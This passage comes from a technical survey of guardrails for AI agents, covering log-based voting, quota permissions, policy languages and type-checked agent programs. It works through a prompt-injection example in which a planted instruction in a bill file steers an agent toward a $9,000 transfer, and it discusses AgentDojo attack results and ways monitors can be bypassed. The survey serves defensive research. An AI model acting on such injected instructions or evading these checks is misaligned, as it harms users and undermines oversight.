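The log, which the paper calls the AgentBus, is an append-only list of typed entries. The agent cycles through four stages, each run by a separate component. In *inferring*, the Driver calls the model with the user's message or the latest result, then appends the model's reply and the action it extracts from that reply. In *voting*, one or more Voters examine the action and append their votes. In *deciding*, the Decider applies the current voting policy and appends either a commit or an abort. In *executing*, the Executor runs the committed action and appends the result, which starts the next cycle. After an abort, the agent goes straight back to inferring.

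| Entry type | Contents | Appended by | Read by |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail | message from a user or another agent | outside parties | Driver |
| InfIn | input sent to the model | not listed | not listed |
| InfOut | the model's reply | Driver | Driver, optionally Voters |
| Intent | proposed action | Driver | Voters |
| Vote | a Voter's verdict | Voters | Decider, optionally Voters |
| Commit | decision to run the action | Decider | Executor |
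| Abort | decision not to run it | Decider | Driver |
| Result | outcome of the action | Executor | Driver |
| Policy | change to a component's rules | outside administrators | all components |

The AgentBus enforces read and append permissions separately for each entry type. The paper's list of permissions omits InfIn, which the Driver presumably appends because it makes the inference call. The list also lets the Executor read commits but not intents, so either a commit has to carry a copy of the action or the Executor needs permission to read intents.

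The components are separate mainly because the Executor runs code that a language model wrote. If that code could also append votes or commits, an injected instruction could make it approve its own actions. Balakrishnan and colleagues therefore put the Executor in a sandbox with selective access to the production environment and no access to the machines that run the other components. The Driver and any model-based Voters exchange text with a model but never execute what it returns. A Voter can also be an ordinary program that applies rules without using a model, which makes it immune to prompt injection.

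Separation also lets an administrator replace Voters while the agent is running. In one demonstration, an administrator added a rule-based Voter after 312 seconds and a model-based one after 655, each time with a Policy entry that changed how the Decider counts votes. Because the change is a log entry, every component applies it at the same point in the log.

### One payment through the log

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a bill, and an attacker has planted an instruction in the file that contains it. The log might look like this:

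| Position | Type | Content |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Mail | request to pay the December bill |
| 1 | InfIn | the request and the standing instructions |
| 2 | InfOut | a reply that includes a call to read the bill |
| 3 | Intent | read the bill file |
| 4 | Vote | approve 3 |
| 5 | Commit | run 3 |
| 6 | Result | text of the bill, with a planted order to send $9,000 to another account |
| 7 | InfIn | the text from 6 |
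| 8 | InfOut | a reply that follows the planted order |
| 9 | Intent | send $9,000 to that account |
| 10 | Vote | reject 9, unknown payee |
| 11 | Abort | do not run 9 |

By position 8, the injection has succeeded against the model, but no money has moved because the Executor acts only on commits. The Driver then reads the abort and calls the model again, and this time the model may not follow the injection. If the Voter had approved the payment, the commit would have been in durable storage before the Executor contacted the bank.

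### A true log and a safe action

The $9,000 might also have gone to a payee the rules allow, in which case the log would be accurate but the money would still be gone. Balakrishnan and colleagues separate these matters with three definitions. Let *L* = ⟨*I*₁, …, *I*ₙ⟩ be the committed intents in order, *E*₀ the initial environment, and *E*ₖ the environment after the Executor has supposedly run the first *k* intents.

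*Consistency* holds if, for every *k* up to *n*, *E*ₖ is what a faithful execution of *I*₁, …, *I*ₖ on *E*₀ would produce.

*Safety* concerns a set *S* of invariants that an administrator wants the environment to satisfy, such as "no money goes to anybody the user doesn't owe". The log is safe if, for every *k*, faithfully executing its first *k* intents produces an environment that satisfies *S*.

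*Enforced-Safety* is the same property with *S* replaced by *S̃*, the approximation of *S* that the Voters enforce. In the example, *S̃* might be "every payee is on a list of known payees".

Safety describes what the committed actions would do if executed faithfully, so the real bank account is safe only if Consistency also holds. The paper derives Consistency from the assumption that the Executor is faithful, and Safety from the assumption that the Voters enforce *S* correctly. Both results follow almost directly from the definitions. The more useful part of the analysis covers what happens when the Voters approve an action they should have stopped.

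Most often, the approved action damages only the environment. For example, the agent overpays the landlord, who is on the list. This violates Safety but not Enforced-Safety or Consistency. The paper calls this the benign case but notes that it can be disastrous if *S̃* is far from *S*, since deleting all of production would also fall under it.

An approved action can also alter the Executor, for instance by adding code that makes it report payments it never made. The Voters still check every later intent against the same rules, so Enforced-Safety holds, but the log no longer matches what happened. The design doesn't prevent this, though an auditor could detect it by comparing the log with an independent source, such as a bank statement.

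The worst outcome is an action that replaces the Voters or the Decider, or changes their rules, because every later intent may then pass. The log can still be accurate, since it lists each bad action and the Executor carries it out as listed. Running the Executor in isolation, under a different identity and on separate infrastructure, is meant to prevent such tampering. In the paper's tests, the Voters and the Decider ran in processes isolated from the Executor, but the Driver ran alongside it. Code that took over the Executor might therefore have been able to forge model replies in the log, although a forged intent would still have needed approval.

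These definitions assume at first that only the agent changes the environment. In practice, other people and programs change it too, so the paper weakens Safety to a rule about single steps: the agent must never take a safe environment to an unsafe one. This restricts what a Voter can usefully check. Suppose a stock counter must not go below zero. A Voter that reads a value of 1 cannot safely approve "subtract 1", because another program may subtract 1 first. It can approve code that locks the counter and subtracts only if the value is positive. The meta-agent in Agentic Redux avoids this problem because it holds the whole state and changes it one step at a time.

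### Replay rebuilds the conversation

Like *The Log is the Agent*, LogAct replays the model's recorded replies (the InfOut entries), so the model's randomness doesn't affect the result. A restarted Driver loads the last snapshot of the conversation, reads the entries after that point, and rebuilds exactly the history the previous Driver had.

If two Drivers ran at once, each would propose its own response to the same message. To prevent this, a new Driver begins by appending a Policy entry that names itself as the only valid Driver. If that entry lands at position 9 and the old Driver's last intent lands at position 10, every reader must ignore that intent. This procedure conflicts with the paper's rule that only administrators may append Policy entries. If permissions depend on an entry's type alone, a Driver that can elect itself can also change the voting policy. An implementation should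 probably give elections a separate entry type.

*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a harness from Amazon that also logs before it acts. A single process, the sequencer, writes the agent's log. It records each model call or tool call before starting it, and computes what to do next as a fold over the log. If the sequencer is killed at any instruction, the next one closes whatever was open and continues, with no separate recovery procedure. The paper states that this recovers only the conversation. An effect on the world and the record of its result are separate operations, and a crash can happen between them.

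### Replay cannot rebuild the outside world

LogAct aims for *at-most-once* execution, because a restarted Executor that reran the committed intents would repeat any actions already completed, such as paying a bill. Instead, the restarted Executor appends a special Result entry recording the restart, and the Driver passes this to the model. The model then proposes actions to find out how far the interrupted work got and to finish or undo it. The Voters review these actions like any other intent.

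When a commit has no result, the log alone doesn't show how far the work got. The payment may never have started, may have stopped halfway, or may have gone through just before the crash. *Agentao* (2026), another harness, requires a permission decision in the trace for every attempted call, and a start event and an end event for every call that runs. If the harness stores the start event durably before the tool runs, a missing start event shows that the call never began. If the start event is present, the payment may still have either stopped halfway or gone through.

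Asking the bank whether a payment went through isn't always enough for an agent to recover without paying twice, as Li (2026) proves in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?*. Suppose a payment request times out, the bank offers no protection against repeats, and the agent's recovery policy always completes the task within a time *T* if the request was lost. The agent must therefore resend a lost request by time *T*. Now suppose the request was instead delayed by more than *T* plus the time a completed payment takes to show up in the account. Until the agent resends, everything it can observe is the same in both cases, so it resends here too, and both payments go through. The agent can avoid this by waiting if it knows an upper limit on the delay, but few services document one.

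Li tested nine models in a sandbox of six simulated services. When a service had completed a write but lost the reply, frontier models instructed to act exactly once duplicated the write in 0.5% of episodes. They checked, found the completed write, and stopped. When the request was still on its way, the same models duplicated it in 56% of episodes because they checked too early. In a variant with delays of up to two hours, a policy that waited an hour before checking avoided duplicates and completed the task in 84% of episodes.

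A better remedy is an *idempotency key*, an identifier attached to a request so that the service executes it at most once, however often it arrives. When Li let every write accept a key, the overall duplicate rate fell from 28% to 4%. In all the remaining duplicates, the agent had sent its first attempt without a key or changed the key when it retried. A write-ahead log could help prevent these duplicates if the harness generated the key and stored it in the Intent entry for later attempts to reuse. The agent's own account is a poor substitute for the log, because in 90% of the episodes with a duplicated effect, the agent reported the task as completed.

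Balakrishnan and colleagues tested recovery on an easier task. An agent computing checksums for 2,000 folders had finished 1,184 when it exceeded its time limit and was stopped. A second agent received the first one's intents, counted the lines in the output file, and found that 816 folders were left. It also noticed that the original code was needlessly slow, rewrote it, and finished the rest in 0.36 seconds. The test shows that an agent can learn from logged intents what its predecessor was trying to do. But the second agent got the count from the output file, and repeating a checksum would have done no harm. The run also committed every action automatically, without any Voters.

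### AgentDojo

The LogAct team tested the Voters on AgentDojo, a prompt injection benchmark from ETH Zurich and Invariant Labs (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It has four simulated environments: an office workspace, Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Each has tools, data, ordinary tasks such as paying a bill or inviting a colleague to a channel, and attacker goals such as sending money to the attacker's account. The benchmark has 97 ordinary tasks in all and pairs each one with every attacker goal in the same environment. The bank's 16 tasks and 9 goals make 144 pairs, and the four environments together give 629 security cases.

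In a security case, the attacker's text sits in data that the agent will read while doing the user's task. Ordinary code then checks the agent's answer and the final state of the environment, such as whether money was transferred. The benchmark doesn't use a language model as judge, because an injection that fools the agent might fool the judge too. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent solves when there is no attack, and attack success rate is the share of security cases in which it carries out the attacker's goal.

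LogAct's main test used a model from 2024, roughly as old as the benchmark. The paper names neither this model nor the newer one it used for comparison.

| Configuration | Attack success | Benign utility | Average latency |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2024 model, no defence | 48.2% | 81.4% | 6.7 s |
| 2024 model, rule-based Voter | 1.4% | 49.5% | 10.6 s |
| 2024 model, rule-based and model-based Voters | 1.4% | 78.4% | 12.2 s |
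| newer frontier model, no defence | 0% | 91.8% | 13.3 s |

The rules stopped nearly all the attacks but also blocked many legitimate actions. A second Voter, running on the same 2024 model, restored most of the lost utility by overriding some rejections. It used few extra tokens because the harness called it only when the rules rejected an intent.

The remaining 1.4% were attacks that needed only a reply, so they produced no Intent entry to vote on. Debenedetti and colleagues describe a similar gap in defences that isolate tools. In their example, hidden text in a hotel listing makes the agent recommend that hotel.

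### How much the numbers show

The fall from 48.2% to 1.4% is weaker evidence about new attacks than it seems, because the rules were created by having a language model study the 2024 model's runs on the same benchmark, including its attacks. LogAct reports no tests on held-out attacks or on attacks designed against the Voters. Even with rules fitted to the benchmark, utility fell by 32 percentage points, which suggests that good rules for open-ended tasks are hard to write.

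Low attack rates are fairly easy to reach on AgentDojo. Its creators warned that a weak defence can stop any particular fixed attack, and wanted researchers to add attacks adapted to each defence. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) found that all five benchmarks it examined still relied on attack templates. In *Indirect Prompt Injections*, Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) used a second model to rewrite tool outputs and leave out suspicious instructions. This simple filter brought attack success on AgentDojo to 0%, but when they adapted their attacks to it, the success rate on the Slack tasks rose to 30%.

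The newer model's 0% attack success rate calls for similar caution. Balakrishnan and colleagues suggest that the model may have seen AgentDojo in training and that its developers probably prepared it for known attacks. A model can also score 0% by failing to act. *Render Before Reading* (2026) reports that no attacks succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5 under its default prompt, but that the model often put off financial actions whose details were incomplete. General passivity is an unlikely explanation for LogAct's newer model, which completed 91.8% of the unattacked tasks. Whatever the reason for the 0%, Voters could not have lowered it on this benchmark.

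The OR policy that restored utility has a more basic weakness. If *R* is the set of intents that the rules approve and *M* the set that the model-based Voter approves, the policy commits everything in *R* ∪ *M*, which gives up the hard guarantee under the rules alone that nothing outside *R* would run. The model-based Voter can only add to the intents that get committed. It can't block one that the rules wrongly approve, because approval by the rules is already enough.

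That Voter is also exposed to prompt injection. By default, LogAct denies model-based Voters access to the environment so that planted text cannot reach them, but in this test the Voter read earlier results from the log, including any injected instructions. It approved none of the harmful actions, although the attacks were aimed at the agent, not at a Voter.

An AND policy would commit only *R* ∩ *M* and keep the guarantee, but it could hardly restore utility, since it would still block everything the rules block. A compromise is to make a few rules binding, such as a cap on payments, and let the model override the rest. If *H* is the set of actions the binding rules allow, the Decider would commit *H* ∩ (*R* ∪ *M*), and nothing outside *H* could run however the model-based Voter votes. LogAct's policies can in principle combine Voters this way, but the paper doesn't test it, so nobody knows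 how much the binding rules would reduce utility.

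## Agenra: permissions that are used up

A monitor can enforce a cap on the size of each payment without memory, because it only has to compare the proposed amount with the cap. A rule such as "send the report once" requires memory, because the second send can be identical to the first, and a check based only on the proposed call would have to allow both or refuse both.

*Agenra* (Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) stores this memory in the permissions. Each permission has a quota, and each use reduces it by one. Agenra combines a policy language with a monitor whose core is written in Lean, a proof assistant that can also compile the functions its proofs are about. Many of the proofs therefore apply to the code that checks live calls.

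### A report that may go out once

In the paper's main example, a user asks an agent to send the public fields of a private report to Alice, at most once. The agent doesn't know Alice's address at the start. A correct run uses five tools:

| Call | Result | Label of the result |
|---|---|---|
| `Read()` | *report*, the private original | Confidential, trusted |
| `Sanitize(report)` | *summary*, its public fields | Public, trusted |
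| `Lookup()` | *record*, Alice's directory entry | Public, trusted |
| `Extract(record)` | *address* | Public, trusted |
| `Send(body: summary, recipient: address)` | the email goes out | |

A sixth tool, `Other`, reads untrusted content, where an attacker can plant instructions to send the raw report, use another address, or send again. The agent refers to results only by name, and the monitor keeps the values, so the agent can't submit the raw report while claiming it is the summary.

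Labels stop the raw report. A label in Agenra is a triple (*s*, *C*, *t*) of a sensitivity level, a set of categories such as "credentials", and a trust flag. When a call uses several values, the monitor *joins* their labels:

(*s*₁, *C*₁, *t*₁) ⊔ (*s*₂, *C*₂, *t*₂) = (max(*s*₁, *s*₂), *C*₁ ∪ *C*₂, *t*₁ ∧ *t*₂)

The join is as sensitive as the more sensitive input, includes every category of either input, and is trusted only if both inputs are. Combining the report with a page from `Other` gives (Confidential, ∅, true) ⊔ (Public, ∅, false) = (Confidential, ∅, false). The policy lets only Public data reach the mail tool, so the agent can't email the combined text.

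`Sanitize` is an exception to the join, because the policy marks its output Public whatever went in. The application's developers vouch for the tool, but nobody proves that it removes every secret.

A Public label alone permits too much, since text from `Other` is Public too. The policy therefore has an *origin rule*, which requires the email body to be a result of `Sanitize`. An early version of the policy lacked this rule. The rule still leaves a gap, because the agent can run `Sanitize` on an attacker's text and mail the result to Alice. A second origin rule closes the gap by requiring the input of `Sanitize` to come from `Read`. The monitor could not have detected either omission, because it has no access to what the user meant.

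### What a permission contains

Formally, a permission is a tuple *p* = (α, *R*, *K*, χ, *m*):

| Part | Meaning | Value for sending the report |
|---|---|---|
| α | the action | `message.send` |
| *R* | the resources it may affect | the address in the slot `target` |
| *K* | the argument names a call may use | `recipient`, `body` |
| χ | limits on argument values | none |
| *m* | the quota | 1 |

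A *slot* is a placeholder for a resource that is not yet known. Only the `destination` field of a successful `Lookup()` can fill the slot `target`, and the permission authorizes no sends until it does. A second lookup that returns the same address changes nothing, but one that returns a different or malformed address makes the slot invalid for the rest of the task. An email with a supposed new address for Alice has no effect on the slot, but a compromised directory could still supply a wrong address.

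Every action needs a matching permission on both the user's list and the application's list. If the user allows two sends and the application allows only one, the monitor refuses the second send.

Between calls, the monitor keeps the state *S* = (*M*, *L*, τ, *B*, *I*, *u*ₚ, *u*ₐ). *M* holds the label of every call the monitor has admitted, *L* records which earlier results each call used, and τ is the trace. *B* holds the addresses now in the slots, and *I* lists the invalid slots. The counters *u*ₚ and *u*ₐ record how much the agent has used of each permission on the user's list and the application's list, respectively.

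### Check, charge, run

When the agent proposes a call, the monitor goes down each list and reserves one unit of the first permission that matches and has quota left. This is *first-fit allocation*. A call with several effects, such as a batch that deletes two files, needs one unit for each effect. The monitor then checks the labels, the origins and any other rules. If a check fails, it discards the reservations and refuses the call. Otherwise, it commits the charges, adds the call to the trace, and only then lets the tool run.

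The monitor never restores used quota, even if the tool fails. Agenra thus provides at-most-once execution, as LogAct does. But if the first `Send` fails, Alice may never get the report, because the agent has no send left and can't restore its own quota.

### How a wider permission blocks a legitimate task

Quotas complicate a routine part of running an agent, which is changing its permissions. Suppose a task may delete file A once and file B once. The list has two permissions with a quota of one each, first for B and then for A. A developer widens the first permission to cover either file. Under first-fit allocation, this has two effects that the developer probably didn't want:

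| Sequence | Permissions {B}, {A} | Permissions {A, B}, {A} |
|---|---|---|
| delete B, then A | both run | both run |
| delete A, then B | both run | the monitor refuses B |
| delete A, then A | the monitor refuses the second | both run |

With the original list, deleting A uses up the second permission and leaves the first for B. With the wider list, deleting A uses up the first permission. The remaining permission doesn't cover B, but it does cover A, so the agent can delete A again (for instance, if someone has recreated it).

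Ordinary testing could easily miss this, because each deletion the old list allowed is still possible in a fresh task, and a trial run that deletes B first succeeds. Adam Barth and John Mitchell described the same effect in 2006 for digital-rights licences, where a more generous licence could stop a customer from playing something they could play before.

Unlike first-fit allocation, assigning A to the permission that covers nothing else would allow the sequence A, B here, although it would still allow two deletions of A. But no allocator can allow every sequence that the permissions could cover if it uses only past calls and can't revise its assignments.

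To prove this, take two permissions, {A, B} and {A, C}, each with a quota of one. The sequence A, B is feasible if A uses {A, C}, and the sequence A, C is feasible if A uses {A, B}. Both sequences start with A, so a deterministic allocator has the same information when it handles A and must make the same choice in both cases. If it uses {A, B}, it can't serve B next, and if it uses {A, C}, it can't serve C, so it fails on one of the two feasible sequences.

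Choosing at random doesn't help much, because the allocator then fails at least half the time on at least one of the two sequences. A monitor could avoid this failure by reassigning earlier charges when a later call needs them. Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues keep first-fit instead, so the order of the list determines which permission is charged, and charges are never reassigned. They then ask which changes to a list are harmless.

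### Revisions that keep every workflow

The paper calls a finite sequence of calls, together with the results that the services return, a *client*. Write Adm(*P*) for the clients that the monitor admits from a fresh task under policy *P*. A revision from *P* to *P*′ preserves clients if

Adm(*P*) ⊆ Adm(*P*′).

The preservation theorem covers three kinds of change. A developer may raise a quota, append a permission to the end of a list, or swap two neighbouring permissions that never match the same action. Any combination of these changes, on either list, preserves every client of finite length. The theorem assumes that the monitor processes one call at a time and that the tools return the same results under both policies.

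The proof is a *simulation*, which runs the old and new monitors side by side and shows that the new one can match every step the old one takes. For raised quotas and appended permissions, the invariant is that every permission on the old list has at least as much quota left on the new list.

The invariant holds at the start, because no quota has gone down. Suppose it holds now and the old monitor admits an action by charging the permission at position *j*. That permission also has quota left on the new list, so the new monitor finds a match at *j* or earlier. If it charges *j*, both lists lose one unit there and the invariant still holds. If it charges an earlier position *k*, the old monitor must have passed over *k* because it had no quota left. The new list can lose a unit at *k* without falling below zero, so the invariant still holds. By induction, it holds for sequences of any length.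 Swapping two permissions that never match the same action only renumbers the charges.

This argument fails at exactly one step for the widened deletion permission. When A arrives, the old monitor skips the first permission, whose quota is intact, because it doesn't match A. The widened permission does match A, so the new monitor uses that quota, which B needs later.

For other revisions with finite quotas, a Python program can propose a relation between old and new counter values, and Lean checks that every step preserves it. Some harmless revisions have no relation that passes this check, so failing to find one does not show that a revision is harmful.

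Agenra tested these methods on 51 revisions made for the paper, including all 24 orderings of a list of four permissions. A separate program enumerated every admitted sequence and showed that 21 revisions preserved all clients and 30 lost at least one. The three structural changes accounted for 16 of the 21, and the checker certified the other five using proposed relations. It certified none of the 30, and replaying the lost workflows on the tools confirmed each loss.

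These results show that the checker works on cases its designers thought of, but not how often such cases arise in real maintenance. The study includes one change from a real agent application, the app builder Dyad, whose developers raised a quota of free messages from five to ten. The checker certified the change, but Dyad refunds the quota when a message fails and renews it after a time, and the model leaves out both. The certificate therefore covers only successful messages within one quota period.

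### Preservation without safety

A revision can preserve every client and still be unsafe. If a developer raises the quota for `Lookup` in the report task from one to two, the agent can confirm Alice's address before sending. Raising the quota for `Send` also preserves every client, and the checker certifies it too. But the new policy admits a second approved send, which the user had ruled out. The inclusion Adm(*P*) ⊆ Adm(*P*′) doesn't limit what else Adm(*P*′) contains.

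Developers have to check for forbidden sequences separately. Agenra does this with a bounded search, which runs the monitor's own functions on every possible sequence up to a chosen length. For the report task with a send quota of one, the search found no violation within eight events, and with a quota of two it found the second send. Searching up to eight events took 154 seconds and about 12 million steps, compared with less than a second for six, so the search suits only small workflows. It also considers only the tool results that the developers supply.

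Trials with live agents add little to the case for Agenra. In 20 attacked runs per model, an unguarded Qwen model sent the raw report 15 times and a Hermes model once. Agenra reduced both to zero, but so did a simple guard that the authors wrote by hand. Qwen delivered the report in 5 of its attacked runs and Hermes in 10, with or without a guard. The attacks never succeeded against three configurations of Claude, even unguarded. The stronger reason to use a system like Agenra is that the hand-written guard provides no way to tell which future changes to its rules would break a workflow.

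### What has to be right besides the proofs

The trusted base is large for a system with verified code at its centre. Unverified Python programs translate the policy, match the agent's names to stored values, pass calls to Lean and run the tools. They must run exactly the call that Lean checked. The trusted base also includes the Lean compiler and runtime.

The application's developers must label the sources correctly and declare every effect of each tool. In one of the paper's tests, the declaration for a batch-deletion tool listed fewer deletions than the tool performed, and the monitor allowed a deletion it should have refused. The agent must also run outside the monitor's process, because the boundary between them relies on Python object identity, which doesn't confine arbitrary Python code.

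The quotas only hold if calls run one at a time, because calls checked simultaneously could together exceed a quota, just as the two agents overspent their shared budget. Agenra prevents this by holding a lock until it has processed each call's result. An agent that normally makes several calls in parallel would have to wait for each one to finish before starting the next.

### Why such questions can be undecidable

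It is rather surprising that Agenra can answer questions about sequences of any length, because a well-known result from 1976 rules this out for permission systems in general. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976), in *Protection in Operating Systems*, modelled permissions as an *access matrix*. It has a row for every subject, such as a process or a user, and a column for every object, such as a file. Each cell holds the rights of that subject to that object. Commands change the matrix, as in this example:

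```
command CONFER_read(owner, friend, file)
  if   own in (owner, file)
  then enter read into (friend, file)
```

A command first tests whether certain rights are present. It may then enter or delete rights, and create or destroy subjects and objects. The *safety question* is whether, from a given matrix, any sequence of commands can enter a particular right into a cell that lacked it. Harrison and colleagues proved that this is undecidable, meaning no algorithm answers it correctly for every system.

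The proof uses the matrix to simulate a Turing machine, a minimal model of computation that reads and writes symbols on an endless tape. Harrison and colleagues represent each cell of the tape by a subject, which owns the subject for the next cell. The symbol in a cell becomes a right that the cell's subject has to itself, and so does the machine's current state. Each command performs one move of the machine and creates a new subject when the machine reaches an unused cell. The right that stands for the final state then appears in the matrix if and only if the machine reaches that state. No algorithm can decide in general whether a Turing machine will reach its final state, so no algorithm can decide the safety question in general.

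Restrictions on the commands can make the question decidable. If no command can create anything, the matrix has finitely many possible contents and an algorithm can search them, although the worst case probably takes exponential time. The question is also decidable if every command performs just one operation. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational Work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, found a mistaken assumption in the proof of how hard the one-operation case is and supplied a corrected proof. Harrison and colleagues considered this case too restrictive to be realistic. They also stressed that their theorem doesn't prevent anyone from proving a particular system safe.

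Agenra avoids undecidability with a much stronger restriction. No tool call or result can change the permission lists, so the agent has no equivalent of `CONFER_read`. The closest thing to a new right is an address in a slot, and only the lookup named in the policy can supply that address.

The remaining task is to find the sequences that fixed lists allow. Finite quotas limit the counters to finitely many values, so four permissions with a quota of one have only 2⁴ = 16 combinations. Addresses can take infinitely many values, but for any one action the monitor only checks which slots contain the address in question, which leaves a finite number of cases. The analysis doesn't restrict what the model computes between calls, because it already covers every order in which the model might propose them.

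CapScope, by contrast, lets agents create sub-agents and give them permissions, which are the two operations that the 1976 proof needs. Its invariant still settles the safety question for every permission beyond the task's limit.

### Policies without memory: Cedar and Progent

The most widely available controls for agents are simpler still, because they decide each request separately. Since March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026), customers of Amazon's cloud service can put a gateway between an agent and its tools that checks every request against rules in Cedar, an open-source policy language. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives a typical rule, shortened here:

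```
permit (principal, action == process_refund, resource)
when { principal.getTag("username") == "John"
       && context.input.amount < 500 };
```

The gateway refuses anything that no rule permits, and a `forbid` rule overrides any number of `permit` rules. The order of the rules has no effect. The AWS page describes this rule as allowing refunds of $500 or less, but the rule refuses a refund of exactly $500. A check for contradictions would not find this error, because the rule is consistent.

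Cedar has no loops and no operations that change state. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* presents it as an advantage that identical requests always get the same decision. This makes policies easier to analyse, but it also means an agent acting for John can refund $499 a hundred times if it can do so once. According to AWS's documentation, policies can use only facts about the user and the inputs of the current call. A limit on the total has to be enforced somewhere else, such as in the refund tool.

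In return, revisions are much easier to check. If every decision depends on the request alone, the gateway admits a sequence exactly when it allows each request in it. Allowing more requests therefore never blocks a sequence that was admitted before, so the problem with the two deletions can't arise. AWS offers a tool that compares two versions of a policy by translating them into logical formulas. In one example, the tool reports that a policy became more permissive when a developer added a condition to an exception. The change looks like a restriction, but the exception now applies to fewer orders.

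*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) uses a similar comparison while the agent is running. Its rules also allow or forbid calls by tool name and arguments, but a language model writes them for each task and proposes updates as the agent learns more. For example, a user asks the agent to do the to-do list in an email. The first policy allows only a search for that email. Once the agent has read the list, it also needs to read other messages and post a summary to Slack. After it finds the user's Slack name, the policy can restrict posts to that name.

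An attacker who fools the updating model could have it add a permission to forward the inbox. Progent therefore compares every proposed policy *P*′ with the current policy *P* using an SMT solver, a program that decides whether logical formulas can be true. Let *A*(*P*) be the set of calls that policy *P* allows. If *A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*), the update narrows the policy and takes effect at once. Any other update counts as an expansion and needs approval, even if it removes more permissions than it adds. The set of allowed calls can never grow without approval, a property that Shi and colleagues call *monotonic confinement*.

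On AgentDojo, Progent reduced attack success from 39.9% to 1.0% and preserved utility. These runs barely test monotonic confinement, because the system approved every expansion automatically. The result mostly measures how well a language model writes policies. The initial policies without updates reduced attack success to 2.5%, and human review of the policies reduced it to 0%. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so a reviewer would have little to do.

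Progent could in principle limit an agent to a single send by removing the permission after the first use. This update would narrow the agent's permissions, so it would need no approval. But a language model would have to propose it, and Shi and colleagues list sending an email among the actions that need no update afterward. Agenra's counter goes down automatically, without a model having to propose the change.

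### Approvals that expire before the effect

Both kinds of policy check a call before it runs, but the facts can change before the call takes effect. Agenra lets a reviewer approve one exact call, and the monitor uses up the approval just before running the tool. However, Agenra's formal model has no step for the reviewer to withdraw an approval.

*Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) studies this gap. In its opening example, an agent prepares a software deployment, then someone revokes the only approval for it. The software and its target haven't changed, so a check for changed files passes and the deployment goes ahead without authority.

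The proposed remedy, *commit-time authorization*, requires a complete and current justification at the moment an effect becomes permanent. The justification has five parts: there is a live approval, the facts it relied on still hold, any work it depends on is finished, it names exactly this effect, and nobody has cancelled the branch of work that the effect belongs to.

All five parts must belong to the same justification. Suppose a manager gives approval 3 for a support ticket at version 7. The ticket then changes to version 8, and the manager gives approval 4 for the new version but later revokes it. Approval 3 is still live, and version 8 is current. A monitor that checked each part separately could combine these two facts and allow a change to version 8 that no live approval covers. One justification must therefore satisfy every condition (∃*J* ∀ conditions), which is a stronger requirement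 than each condition having some justification (∀ conditions ∃*J*).

The service that stores the ticket repeats the check in the same database transaction as the write, so that nothing can change between them. This is harder if a different service stores the approvals. That service can issue a *reservation* for the exact effect, which works only once and expires after a set time. In Agenra's terms, a reservation is a permission with a quota of one and a deadline. Revoking the approval doesn't cancel a reservation that was already issued, so the effect may still happen until the deadline, plus a small allowance for differences between clocks.

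A short deadline reduces this risk but may leave too little time to act. In one test with sixteen workers in a single process, almost no writes finished within 100 milliseconds. When each worker had its own process and the workers wrote to different tickets, more than 95% of writes did.

Santos-Grueiro also collected 17 security advisories about approvals in three coding and assistant products. In five, an approval remained in effect after something changed, such as a script being rewritten. In the other twelve, nothing had changed, but the product ran something the approval didn't cover, such as the same command with different arguments. Thirteen of the advisories concern one product, so they show that both failures occur but not how common they are. Binding an approval to the exact call would matter more for the group of twelve than checking it late.

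Telling a model that the facts have changed can prevent unauthorized effects, but only if the notice arrives before the model requests the write. Five models worked on tasks in which an approval or another relevant fact changed midway, with a prompt that stated the authorization rule. Without notice of the change, GPT-5.6 Sol completed 25 of 36 tasks with an unauthorized effect, and Claude Sonnet 5.5 completed 30. With a timely notice, these numbers fell to one and zero. In a test with the agent framework LangChain, the owner changed the facts after the model had requested a write and before the framework ran it, so the model had no turn in which to react. LangChain applied all 28 such writes, and the protected version refused all 28.

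The refusals follow from the design, because the service and the test's scoring apply the same rule. Lean proofs cover the formal model but not the Python services that implement it. The guarantee fails if the policy omits a relevant fact or an effect bypasses the protected service.

Unless the policy makes an approval single-use, commit-time authorization doesn't limit how often an agent may use it, so an application like the report task would still need a quota. The application would also need a mail service that can check the approval and accept the message in one step. If the mail service can't do this, the harness can only check the approval as late as possible before it hands over the email.

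## Checking an agent's program before it runs

The monitors described so far examine one proposed call at a time, after earlier calls have taken effect. Some agents instead write a short program that makes several calls and computes with the results in between. The harness can pass this whole program to a *type checker* before running any of it. A type checker is the part of a compiler that works out what kind of value each expression produces and rejects the program if the kinds don't fit together.

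Type checkers catch errors such as adding a number to a name. In some languages, types also record what code may do to the outside world. A harness built on such a language can refuse to run a program that might write to a file, even if the line that does so would rarely run.

### A bibliography with no invented entries

In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) give the example of an agent that searches the literature and writes a bibliography file. Every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. An agent with an ordinary code interpreter could break this rule by writing a made-up entry straight into the file. Replacing the interpreter with a single tool that fetches an entry and appends it would prevent this, but then the agent couldn't compute with the entries. To find the earliest paper, for example, the model would have to read them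 one by one.

Their system, ELBA, lets the agent write Haskell programs with a small library. In simplified form, it has three functions:

```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

The first returns the identifiers of matching papers, the second fetches the entry for one identifier, and the third adds an entry to the file.

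`BibIO` is an *effect type*. A computation of type `BibIO a` may use these three operations and any calculation that has no effects, and it produces a value of type `a`. Empty brackets in place of `a` mean that it produces no useful value. Haskell's own file and network functions have a different effect type, `IO`, and the compiler rejects an `IO` computation inside a `BibIO` program.

`Trusted` is an *abstract type*, which means that only the library can construct its values. The agent can therefore obtain a `Trusted Bib` only from `dblpFetchBib`. This restricts what the agent can pass to the operations that the effect type allows.

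The harness requires the agent's program to have type `BibIO ()`. This one passes:

```
do hits <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   case hits of
     []      -> return ()
     doi : _ -> do entry <- dblpFetchBib doi
                   appendToBibFile entry
```

Neither of these does:

```
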